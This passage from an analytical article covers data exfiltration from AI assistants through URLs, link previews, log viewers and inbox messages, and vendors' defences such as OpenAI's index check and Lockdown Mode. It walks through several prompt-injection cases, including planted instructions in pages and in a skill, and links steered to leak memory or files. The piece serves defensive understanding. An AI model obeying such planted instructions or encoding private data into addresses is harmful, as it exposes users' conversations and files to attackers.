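Rehberger kept finding ways around ChatGPT's first check, which dated from December 2023, and presented some at the Black Hat Europe conference in 2024. A stronger version that stopped those attacks appeared around August 2025, according to Embrace The Red. OpenAI explained its rule on 28 January 2026 in a blog post and a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

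According to OpenAI, the check has four steps:

1. A crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the addresses of public pages and images. It has no access to anyone's conversations, account or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to fetch something automatically, a program looks for the exact address in the crawler's index.
3. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads it without asking the user.
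4. If not, the program either tells ChatGPT to try a different website or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

The comparison covers the whole address, not just the site. Suppose the crawler has recorded only the first of these two placeholders:

```
https://news.example/story
https://news.example/story?note=PRIVATE-TEXT
```

ChatGPT can open the first address automatically but not the second, although both requests would go to the same server. A CSP's image rule would allow both or block both, because a browser ignores the query when it compares an address with the list.

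OpenAI reasons that an address which was public independently of a conversation is unlikely to contain that conversation's secrets. The crawler has no access to the private data in a conversation, so that data doesn't affect which addresses are in the index. If a planted instruction makes the model write a passport number into an address, that address will almost certainly not be in the index, because nobody had a reason to publish it. OpenAI claims only that a leak is "much less likely". An exception is possible if, for example, somebody posted a private link on a public forum, but then anyone could already have found it there.

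Attackers can add to the index by publishing pages for the crawler to find, but they have to choose those addresses before they know the secret. GitHub relied on a similar argument for Camo's signatures in 2017. OpenAI and Rehberger both acknowledge that the choice of which public address to fetch can still reveal a little. Rehberger doesn't consider the problem solved, but he calls the check a significant improvement because it makes attacks more complicated.

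He also understands that once a user has entered an address in a message, ChatGPT accepts it for the rest of that chat. This is narrower than the rule Wu and colleagues found in early 2024, which accepted addresses from anywhere in the conversation, including web pages. Some such exception is needed because people ask about pages that no crawler can see, such as a document shared by private link. The exception is less safe when the user pastes in text somebody else wrote.

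### Why OpenAI doesn't rely on a list of sites

OpenAI considers it insufficient to let ChatGPT open links only to well-known websites, because a trusted site can redirect a request to an attacker's site and because a strict list causes so many false alarms that people learn to ignore them.

Checking the exact address makes redirects much less dangerous. A trusted site may still send ChatGPT elsewhere, but the site has received only an address that was already public, so it has no private text to pass on. The check also helps against relays. To submit somebody's emails to a Google Form, as Superhuman's assistant did, the model has to put them in the address, and no crawler would have recorded that address. Salesforce's lapsed domain would also have been much less useful to its new owner under this rule.

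OpenAI also avoids reviewing sites one by one, but it has to crawl a large part of the web and keep the index current. Most companies that build chatbots lack the resources to do this. The index will also miss some harmless addresses. It may not include a page published an hour ago, and it won't include most addresses that a site creates on demand, such as those for a page of search results or a chart whose figures are in the address.

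OpenAI's objection about false alarms therefore also applies to its own check. An index of the public web should cause fewer warnings than a short list of sites, but OpenAI gives no figures for how often users see them. The check probably causes little trouble for people reading ordinary articles and more for people working with new or private pages.

### The warning and the guarantee

The warning is a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". It tells the user that the link is not verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It shows the address and lets the user copy or open the link. If something looks wrong, OpenAI advises leaving the link closed and asking the model for another source or a summary.

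ChatGPT's dialog improves on the "Show Image" button that Anthropic gave Claude in 2023, which appeared for every outside image. The dialog appears only when an address has failed a check, and it describes the risk. A one-click leak remains possible, because a user in a hurry may open the address anyway. A careful user may recognise some of their own words in the address, but it can also carry data in a form that nobody would recognise.

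OpenAI guarantees that the agent will not quietly leak user-specific data through the URL itself when it fetches resources. "Quietly" excludes leaks that the user approves in the dialog, and "through the URL itself" excludes, for instance, private text that an agent types into a form on a public page. The guarantee also covers only fetching, so it doesn't apply to a program that contacts a server in some other way.

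OpenAI also doesn't promise that web pages are free of misleading content or harmful instructions, or that browsing is safe in every other way.

OpenAI's engineers can test a guarantee this narrow, since an address is either in the index or not. Outsiders can read a website's CSP, but they can't inspect OpenAI's index, so they have to try addresses and see what happens, as Rehberger did with the earlier check.

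### Where OpenAI applies the check

OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection*, which OpenAI published in March 2026, explains why the company wanted a defence that works after an attack has fooled the model. The most effective attacks OpenAI sees now resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people through plausible stories. In 2025, outside researchers reported one such attack, disguised as a routine email about a company's restructuring. It worked half the time in tests with one particular user request.

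Many security vendors recommend a classifier that screens material before the assistant reads it. OpenAI says such classifiers usually miss fully developed attacks of this kind, because spotting them is as hard as spotting a lie, and the classifier often lacks the necessary context. It compares the assistant to a customer-service employee who can issue refunds. Some customers will deceive the employee, so the company's systems limit how much the employee can give away. OpenAI says that in most of the attacks it knows of, the model refuses because of its safety training, and Safe Url is meant for the rest.

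In the same post, OpenAI says Safe Url detects when information the assistant learned in the conversation would be sent to a third party. The index check described in January is cruder. It detects whether an address is new, not whether it contains private information, so it also stops harmless new addresses.

OpenAI uses the same mechanism in two other products. In Atlas, its web browser, the check applies when the assistant navigates to a page or saves a bookmark, presumably because the user may open the bookmark later. In Deep Research, which reads many web pages and writes a report on them, it applies to searches as well as navigation. OpenAI doesn't explain in the post how it can check a search query, which is usually new text, against an index of addresses.

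Canvas and ChatGPT Apps need a different safety control because they let ChatGPT create and use working applications. An application can build an address while it runs, after the model has finished writing, so a check on the model's text could miss it. OpenAI runs these applications in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

The list of products matters because Rehberger worries that some product teams at OpenAI may not know about the check or adopt it, a problem he writes that he has often seen in his own work. There is some evidence of it here. PromptArmor reported the Codex leak through a Google Form almost three months after OpenAI described the check. No independent crawler could have recorded an address containing a user's emails, so Codex was probably not applying the check to that image.

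Data could also leave ChatGPT without a link being fetched. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a hidden internet connection from the isolated environment in which ChatGPT runs code. A single malicious prompt, or a customised version of ChatGPT whose maker had planted the instructions, could have used it to leak the user's messages and uploaded files. The Hacker News (2026) reports that OpenAI fixed the flaw on 20 February and that there is no evidence of malicious use. Even a perfect index would not have helped, because the data never went through the check.

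### Lockdown Mode

On 13 February 2026, a week before that repair, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, a setting that switches risky features off instead of checking what they do. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) presents it as a tool for a small group of users, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations. It is off by default, and at first only organisations on certain plans could use it. In June OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts and small businesses.

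OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, a help page, sets out the current limits:

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | ChatGPT reads only stored copies of pages |
| Images | ChatGPT doesn't fetch them from the web and may not show them in ordinary answers, but users can still upload and generate them |
| Deep Research | Off |
| Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites | Off |
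| Canvas | Users can't give its code access to the network |
| File downloads | Off, though ChatGPT can still work on files that the user uploads |
| Apps on personal accounts | ChatGPT can't contact outside services or change anything in them where this conflicts with the mode's protections |
| Apps in organisations' managed workspaces | The administrator decides |
| Codex | No change to its network access |

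The rule on browsing is stricter than the index check. OpenAI says that no live request leaves the network it controls, so a website's owner doesn't even learn which page ChatGPT read. If that is true, browsing satisfies the noninterference condition from the previous section, because outside servers receive nothing, whatever private data the conversation contains. The drawback for users is that search results may be out of date or missing.

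Apps are harder to lock down because people need them for work, and in a managed workspace the mode doesn't automatically disable them. OpenAI advises administrators to enable only apps they trust. Even with a trusted app, it advises against letting ChatGPT write anything unless they can confirm that an attacker couldn't see the result. Reading from a trusted app is less likely to let data out, but it gives ChatGPT more private data that could leave by another route. Applying the advice on writing would have revealed Superhuman's mistake with Google Forms, but administrators have to check every app they allow in this way.

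Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode because its restrictions are deterministic and don't depend on an AI system that an attacker could also fool. He added that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, said that the mode is not for everyone, but that people at higher risk should find it worth losing some features. These positions are compatible because a skilled attacker could get past the default settings, but ordinary users are less likely than executives to face one, even though their chats may be just as private.

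OpenAI also put an "Elevated Risk" label on certain features in ChatGPT, Atlas and Codex that connect to the network. The label informs users of the risk but does not block anything. In Codex, it appears beside the setting that gives the agent internet access, where a developer can also restrict the domains the agent may contact. OpenAI plans to remove each label once it judges that its defences have reduced the risk enough for general use.

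OpenAI says on its help page that Lockdown Mode does not guarantee that data can't leak, and names enabled apps, unforeseen combinations of features and newly discovered techniques as remaining risks. Researchers at Check Point found a way round the mode within months. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that specially crafted content in ChatGPT's preview of HTML code could get round the restrictions. 송 (2026), in *체크포인트, 챗GPT 락다운 모드 뚫었다…팝업 허점 하나로 대화·파일 빼낼 수 있었다*, reports that the fault lay in how the preview handled pop-up windows, and that OpenAI patched it on 18 September. In the ChatGPT Classic app, the attack required no action from the user. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that the attack gave access to the entire chat history.

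The preview is part of the program that displays ChatGPT's answers, so limiting web browsing to stored pages could not contain it. The flaw also exposes a weakness in the design of Lockdown Mode, which is a list of prohibitions in Saltzer and Schroeder's sense. It switches off or limits particular features, so its designers had to think of every feature that could reach the network. If the mode had denied network access by default, the preview would have had none until somebody approved it. The block would still have to work, as the failures of the code sandboxes at OpenAI and Microsoft show.

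### Claude's web-fetch rule

Anthropic released a tool in September 2025 that lets Claude retrieve web pages, and Claude's own app uses it when the user turns on web search. The tool refuses any address that Claude has composed itself. As of June 2026, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for developers, said that an address must already have appeared in one of these places:

- a message from the user;
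- a result from a tool that the developer's own software runs;
- the results of an earlier web search or web fetch.

The tool also refuses addresses that come from code Claude runs in Anthropic's sandbox, where a program could easily build an address from private text.

This rule needs no crawler, and it lets Claude open a new or private page as soon as the user supplies the address. When the tool came out, Willison (2025) considered the ban on addresses composed by the model its most protective part, because the usual attack relies on the model building an address out of private data. When he tried to get the Claude app to open such an address, the tool refused.

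Willison had hoped the check would allow only addresses typed by the user. Developers often put an email or a document into the same message as the user's question, so text that the software labels as a user message may come from a stranger. Tool results may also contain a stranger's text. ChatGPT's check had the same weakness in early 2024.

In July 2026 Ayush Paul published an attack that used another of the permitted sources. Claude could open links it found in pages it had already fetched, so the owner of a hostile website could decide which addresses Claude was allowed to open next. Paul's demonstration site obtained the user's name, home city and employer from Claude's memory of past conversations. Willison (2026) reports that Anthropic paid Paul no reward, saying it had already identified the problem internally. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links in the pages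 it fetches.

Anthropic's documentation had listed earlier fetch results as a permitted source of addresses since the tool's release, ten months before Paul's post, and had warned of a "residual risk". Anthropic presumably accepted that risk because people read the web by following links. Claude now has to find the next page through a search or get its address from the user, which is inconvenient for someone who wants it to trace an article's references.

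*The Read-Only Lie*, by the blogger dyb, argues that although Claude's tool could only read pages, each request to read one also sent information out. On this view, Anthropic closed one channel but left the underlying condition in place, as it is in any assistant that combines a memory with live browsing. The change still took a good deal of control away from attackers, because the next address Claude fetches must now come from the user or a search engine. It also brought Anthropic's rule closer to OpenAI's, since a search engine, like OpenAI's crawler, normally finds pages without seeing the user's conversation.

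The table compares what happens to different addresses under each rule, as the companies and Willison describe them.

| Address | ChatGPT's usual check | ChatGPT in Lockdown Mode | Claude's app since July 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| A public page in OpenAI's index | Opens | Stored copy, if available | Opens if the user gave the address or a search returned it |
| A private page whose address the user typed | Opens, as Rehberger understands it | No live request | The rule permits it |
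| A new page, linked from a page the assistant has read | Warning or refusal until the crawler finds it | No live request | Refusal, unless a search also returns it |
| An address the model wrote from private data | Warning or refusal | No live request | Refusal |

Developers who build Anthropic's tool into their own products can restrict it further. Anthropic suggests that those concerned about leaks turn the tool off, cap the number of requests (there is no default cap) or limit it to named domains. Willison calls the domain limit a much stronger protection, provided that none of the domains can pass data to an attacker, which he concedes is tricky to establish.

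## Requests made outside the chat window: previews, log viewers and clicked links

OpenAI and Anthropic check a web address before their assistants open it. But people also talk to assistants in Slack or Telegram, developers read stored answers on a log page, and some assistants write emails. In each case another program displays the text and may make requests that the chat program's checks don't cover. Researchers have shown leaks through all three. They have also argued with Google and Microsoft about how far a vendor must protect users from links in an assistant's answer.

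### Link previews

When someone posts a link in a messaging app, the app usually fetches the page so it can show the title and a picture underneath. Slack calls this unfurling, and by default its servers do it for every link in a message, whether a person or a program posted it. The preview request contains the same address as a click would, so a link that would leak data when clicked can leak it without anyone clicking.

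Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explained in August 2024 how link previews can leak private data. Willison (2024) admitted that he hadn't thought of this kind of leak. An output filter that removes only images doesn't stop it, because Slack will fetch a plain web address. A CSP doesn't stop it either, because the request comes from Slack's servers rather than the reader's browser. Previews can also bring planted instructions to the model, as they did in the experiment by Lan and colleagues.

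A program that posts to Slack can switch off previews for a message by attaching two settings, one for links and one for media such as images. Slack then fetches nothing for that message. This control is deterministic, and readers lose only a title and a picture. However, Slack fetches previews by default, which is the opposite of Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe defaults. A programmer who doesn't know about the problem will leave previews on, and the messages will look normal.

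Anthropic's own programmers left link previews on in a sample Slack connector that the company published. The connector was based on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of giving AI models access to outside tools, and an administrator could restrict it to posting in one private channel. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* points out that people might then think it safe to let the assistant post without supervision, because only colleagues could read the result. In Rehberger's demonstration, Claude posted a link in the private channel that contained a message copied from a different channel. When Slack fetched the preview, the message was sent to Rehberger's server.

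Rehberger reported this on 27 May 2025. Two days later Anthropic archived the connector, though he couldn't tell whether his report was the reason. Anthropic no longer fixes security flaws in it, so anyone still using it has to add the two missing settings or find a replacement. At the time of the advisory, people were downloading it more than 14,000 times a week. Some were probably repeat downloads, so the number of exposed organisations is unknown. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the flaw's severity at 9.3 out of 10, while Rehberger rated it 7.5.

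In 2026 PromptArmor tried to find out how many combinations of assistant and app have this problem by inviting readers of *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* to test their own. A website recorded every preview request it received, and readers could then report which agent had written the link. They could also report combinations that had produced no request. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent that people often control through messaging apps, was exposed in its default setup on Telegram, though it has a setting that switches the previews off. According to Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, Microsoft Teams with agents from Copilot Studio and Slack with certain bots were also susceptible.

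A request in the website's log is good evidence that an app fetched a link. The rest of the data is weaker. The readers volunteered and supplied the agents' names themselves, and a combination of agent and app reported as safe may have been safe only because its owner had changed a setting. The test didn't measure how easily a stranger could get each agent to write a leaking link, but it does show that the same agent can be safe in one app and exposed in another.

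Apostol's article places most of the responsibility on the messaging platforms. PromptArmor divides it more evenly, saying that platforms should let developers control previews and that developers should use that control or pass the choice on to their users. PromptArmor also wants platforms to allow separate settings for each chat or channel. An administrator at a company with several bots could then switch previews off in the channels where the bots post, without relying on each bot's author to remember.

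### A blocked answer in OpenAI's log viewer

Developers who build products with OpenAI's API can look through past conversations on OpenAI's website. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes how this log page could leak data that a product itself had protected.

PromptArmor built a mock version of a tool that banks use to check the identity of new customers. The tool combined material from six sources, including the customer's personal details and web text containing planted instructions. The model followed the instructions and wrote an image address containing the customer's data. A second model judged each answer before display and flagged this one, so the tool didn't show it. When a developer later opened the flagged conversation on OpenAI's log page, the page displayed the answer as formatted Markdown, and the developer's browser requested the image.

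The control in the bank's tool worked, but it also drew a developer's attention to the dangerous answer, and other controls can do the same. PromptArmor shows an answer from Perplexity, an AI search company, after Perplexity's sanitizer had removed an image. The remaining text was odd and empty, so a user could reasonably give it a thumbs-down, which might lead a developer to review it. Whether the product uses a sanitizer, a strict CSP or plain text makes no difference, because none of these applies to a page on OpenAI's website.

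PromptArmor found that several of OpenAI's pages for trying out new agents also loaded outside images, as did a starter application that OpenAI gives developers to build on. Even after a flaw in a starter application is fixed, developers who have already copied the code have to correct their own copies.

PromptArmor sent its report on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that receives such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd's staff asked several rounds of questions, then closed the report as "not applicable" on 4 December, before OpenAI had seen it. After PromptArmor published the findings, OpenAI confirmed the flaw, and on 22 January 2026 it reopened the report and indicated a fix was under way. PromptArmor has not recorded a completed fix, so the flaw may still be open. Until OpenAI confirms one, developers would do better to read suspicious conversations in a program that shows plain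 text and loads nothing.

OpenAI published its explanation of ChatGPT's address check only six days after reopening the report. Running the same check on the log page would almost certainly have stopped this leak. The case, like the Codex leak, therefore supports Embrace The Red's concern that some developers at OpenAI might not know about the check.

### Copilot Cowork and the user's own inbox

Copilot Cowork is a Microsoft agent that carries out longer office tasks, such as writing reports, arranging meetings and sending messages. Microsoft's documentation says Cowork "asks for your permission before taking sensitive actions", such as sending an email. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that Cowork sent emails and Teams messages without asking when the recipient was the person using it, and that users had no setting to change this.

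Under this exception, a message could disclose data even though it went only to the user. It could contain images from outside sites, which Outlook or Teams requested when the user opened it. During EchoLeak, one of the few controls that held was that Copilot couldn't send email without the user. Cowork's permission rule was based on who would receive a message and didn't account for what the receiving program would do with it.

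The attack could expose whole files. Microsoft 365 can create download links that work for anyone who has them, and Cowork could obtain such links for the user's files. An outsider who received the links could download the files.

The planted instructions came in a skill, a file of directions that tells an agent how to do a particular job. Users often find skills online and upload them. In PromptArmor's test, five lines of an 81-line skill were hostile, and the attack succeeded in all five trials. That is a small sample, since even a true success rate of 55 per cent would produce five successes in a row about one time in 20. Instructions are also easier to hide in a skill than in an email, because the agent is supposed to follow a skill's directions. PromptArmor got the same result with Claude Opus 4.7, which was then more capable than some of the models Cowork could choose automatically.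 Opus 4.7 collected more files than the automatic setting had.

A watchful user could have done little about the attack, because Cowork listed the actions it had taken but didn't show the content of the message, even when the user clicked on that step. Cowork can also run scheduled tasks with nobody watching, and the weekly review of recent work that triggered the attack is the sort of task people schedule.

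PromptArmor presents this as a risk in the product's design rather than a specific bug, and reports no fix from Microsoft. Willison (2026) summarised the case on 26 May as an example of the biggest challenge in designing such agents, stopping attackers from getting data out. The exposure may remain, but administrators can reduce it by blocking downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites so that Cowork can't obtain the links. This greatly restricts employees, who can then view those files only in a browser and can't print them or open them in Word or Excel.

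PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) further recommends that an administrator review every skill before anyone uses it, which could have caught the five hostile lines. It also recommends forbidding employees to choose "Don't ask again" when Cowork requests permission. That rule is sensible for messages to other people, but it would not have prevented this attack, because Cowork never asked for permission.

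### The dispute over clicked links

In October 2025 Checkmarx, which sells software security testing tools, reported leaks in AI assistants to Google and Microsoft. Neither company agreed to a fix. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* prints both replies, which concern different problems.

The report to Google was about links. Google's sanitizer stops Gemini from showing outside images, but an attacker could still get Gemini to write a link with private data in its address and hope the user clicks it. Google closed the report after four days with the status "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", though its reply didn't explain why a fix would be infeasible. Google argued that the risk was not severe enough for its security team to impose formal tracking on the product's developers, and that its reward programme covers only flaws that "substantially affect the confidentiality or integrity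 of user data". This fits Google's guide for researchers, under which "Won't fix" means a decision not to track the issue as a separate security bug.

Checkmarx calls Google's answer acceptable but says Google should then warn users, because the decision leaves them to manage the risk. Google already checks links in Gemini's answers with Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous sites, but Checkmarx considers this protection incomplete because an attacker can register a new domain that the service hasn't yet flagged.

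The companies argue that a click is the user's own decision. SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* reports that Google rewards people who find attacks that leak sensitive information "without user approval". Google took a similar position that month on another Gemini flaw, which involved hidden text in emails and calendar invitations. According to Android Authority's *Google says it won't fix Gemini security flaw* (2025), Google dismissed the problem as social engineering and left users to deal with it.

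Clicking a link is poor evidence of approval, because the user has agreed to visit a site but not to send it the contents of an email. The risk also differs from ordinary phishing, in which a link's address can contain only what the sender already knew. An assistant can put anything it has read into a link's address, so the click alone can give away a secret, even if the user closes the page at once and types nothing.

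Google removed all links from its Vertex AI tool in 2023, but a general assistant without links couldn't give its users working references. OpenAI's index check and warning dialog are a compromise, and few companies are better placed than Google to check addresses against an index of the public web. Google would still need an exception for private documents, because their addresses aren't in any public index. It could allow addresses that appear exactly in the user's own files or email. An attacker could put links there too, but, as with OpenAI's index, these could reveal very little.

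In 2025 Tenable, another security company, found that text planted in a user's search history could make Gemini answer "Hello" with a link that leaked saved information or the user's location. Tenable reports that Google fixed this flaw and two related ones. The attack also depended on how Gemini treated the search history, so the fix may not have changed how Gemini handles links. *Gemini Agent Security Risks*, an assessment by the security vendor Adversa AI, still lists leaks through links in Gemini as an unfixed problem.

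Microsoft and Checkmarx disagreed about a zero-click leak through an image. Microsoft closed the report on 4 November 2025, saying that the attack needed several actions users don't normally take, didn't work reliably in every environment, and had to get past warnings. It also cited "Workplace Trust", the assumption that people review and trust the code they choose to run. It probably meant Workspace Trust, a feature of VS Code, since Checkmarx's demonstration stole an access key from a programmer's working environment. Checkmarx replies that the assistant only has to read an article or other page the attacker controls, though it concedes that arranging this can be complicated. Microsoft passed the report to its engineers to look for ways to make the behaviour clearer to users.

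Checkmarx expects Microsoft to refuse to fix leaks through clicked links as well, but that is a guess. On Microsoft's published scale for flaws in AI systems, an attack that takes another user's data is "Critical" if it needs no action from the user and "Important" if it needs "one or more clicks", so a one-click leak is still a vulnerability. Microsoft was stricter than its scale with SearchLeak, which it called critical although the victim had to click.

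### Whether people heed warnings

If vendors make users responsible for the links they click, a warning is often the only control left. Google lists user confirmation among its deterministic defences, but only the prompt follows a fixed rule. The user's answer is unpredictable, so the protection is only as reliable as the user's attention.

There is little direct evidence on how people respond to link warnings in chatbots. *Safety Nudges* (2026), a study of warnings about risky chatbot advice, provides somewhat related evidence. One participant reacted differently in two conversations. In the first, the chatbot gave probabilities of 50, 25, 15 and 10 per cent for four possible equipment faults, and after the warning it conceded that it had not measured these figures. In the second, the chatbot proposed a personal investment strategy, and the participant kept asking for specific instructions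 despite a high-severity warning. Afterwards the participant called the warning helpful and promised to consult a professional before acting.

One person's behaviour doesn't prove anything about people in general, and deciding whether to trust advice is a different task from deciding whether to open a link. Still, the second conversation is a reason to be cautious about judging a warning by asking users whether it helped. This participant would have said yes, but their logged behaviour did not change. Resolving to be more careful after clicking a leaking link doesn't prevent the leak, because the data leaves at the moment of the click.

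A warning also has to help people judge whether a link is safe. Google advises Gemini users to avoid clicking links from untrustworthy sources. That advice works for an email with a visible sender, but in an answer the apparent source is Gemini. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* describes this as a transfer of trust, in which hostile content gains credibility by appearing in ChatGPT's familiar format. That content can include fake security warnings, so a real warning should appear in a part of the screen where the model can't write, such as the separate dialog that OpenAI uses.

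A program must also decide which links need a warning. Google Colab, a service for writing and running code, shows a confirmation page before it opens a link from its assistant. Embrace The Red found that Colab skipped this page for Google's own domains, including the domain of a service where an outsider could collect data. A list of links that need no warning can therefore have the same flaw as a CSP's list of permitted sites.

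### Who could have prevented each leak

The party best placed to prevent each leak was the one that decided what the displaying program would request.

| Leak | Best placed to prevent it | Could have reduced the risk | Could do little |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slack previews with Anthropic's connector | Anthropic, as the connector's author, by switching previews off | Slack, with a safer default for messages from programs; an administrator, by correcting or replacing the connector | The user, because Slack fetches the link as soon as the message arrives |
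| OpenAI's log page | OpenAI, by showing stored answers without outside images | The application's developers, by reading flagged answers as plain text | The application's users, who never see the log |
| Copilot Cowork | Microsoft, by asking before every message or blocking outside images in the agent's messages | An administrator, by reviewing skills and restricting downloads | The user, because Cowork hid the message's content |
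| A clicked link in Gemini | Google, by checking unfamiliar addresses before making them clickable | The user, by not opening unfamiliar links | An administrator, unless the company blocks unfamiliar sites |

Better training of the model would have reduced the risk in every row but not eliminated it. In three of the four rows, one company supplied both the assistant or model and the page or program that displayed its text, so it could have coordinated the two on its own. The Slack case is harder because Slack can detect that a program posted a message, but not whether a language model wrote the text or what the model had read beforehand. Anthropic could assume that a model was involved when its connector posted a message, but the connector didn't use the setting that would have told Slack not to preview the links.

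### Keeping a label on stored and forwarded text

Cleaning the text once, before storing or sending it, may not protect every program that later displays it, because text that is safe in one program can be unsafe in another. The developer who writes the filter can't know what all those programs will be, especially since a company may add a new log viewer years after it stored the conversation.

A more durable approach is to keep a label with the text that records where it came from. It would work roughly like this:

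1. The software that calls the model labels each answer as the work of a model, and records whether the model had read untrusted material or private data.
2. Every program that stores, forwards or quotes the answer copies the label.
3. A program that displays the answer reads the label. If the text is untrusted, it loads no outside images, fetches no previews and checks each link before making it clickable.

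The surrounding software has to add the label, because a model following an attacker's instructions might leave it out. Each program that displays the output can then apply a rule that suits it, so whoever writes the first filter no longer has to predict all of those programs.

Slack's option to switch off previews is a simple form of such a label, since it sends an instruction with a message and Slack follows it. But the instruction applies only to that message. If an employee copies the link into a new one, Slack treats the link as the employee's own and, by default, fetches it.

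OpenAI's log page hardly needs labels on individual answers, because a model wrote all of them and the page could treat every one as untrusted. Labels matter more in inboxes, which mix an agent's messages with those of colleagues and customers. A label in an email is useful only if the recipient's program checks for it. Microsoft could arrange this between Cowork, Outlook and Teams fairly easily, but a message sent to another company's mail program might lose its protection.

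Labels can also become too common to be useful. If assistants draft most of a company's email and every draft counts as untrusted, employees will lose the pictures in most of their messages and ask the administrator to turn the rule off. Recording what the model had read helps, because a model that has seen only public pages has no private data to leak, and a program could show its images as usual. An assistant with a long-term memory or access to a mailbox has usually seen more than public pages, so its messages would keep the restrictions.

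Developers also have to decide what a program should do with unlabeled text. In a log or a channel that only agents write to, the program should load nothing, because a missing label most likely means someone forgot it. In an ordinary inbox, the same rule would block the pictures in nearly all of today's email, so developers would have to start by labeling messages from the company's own agents.
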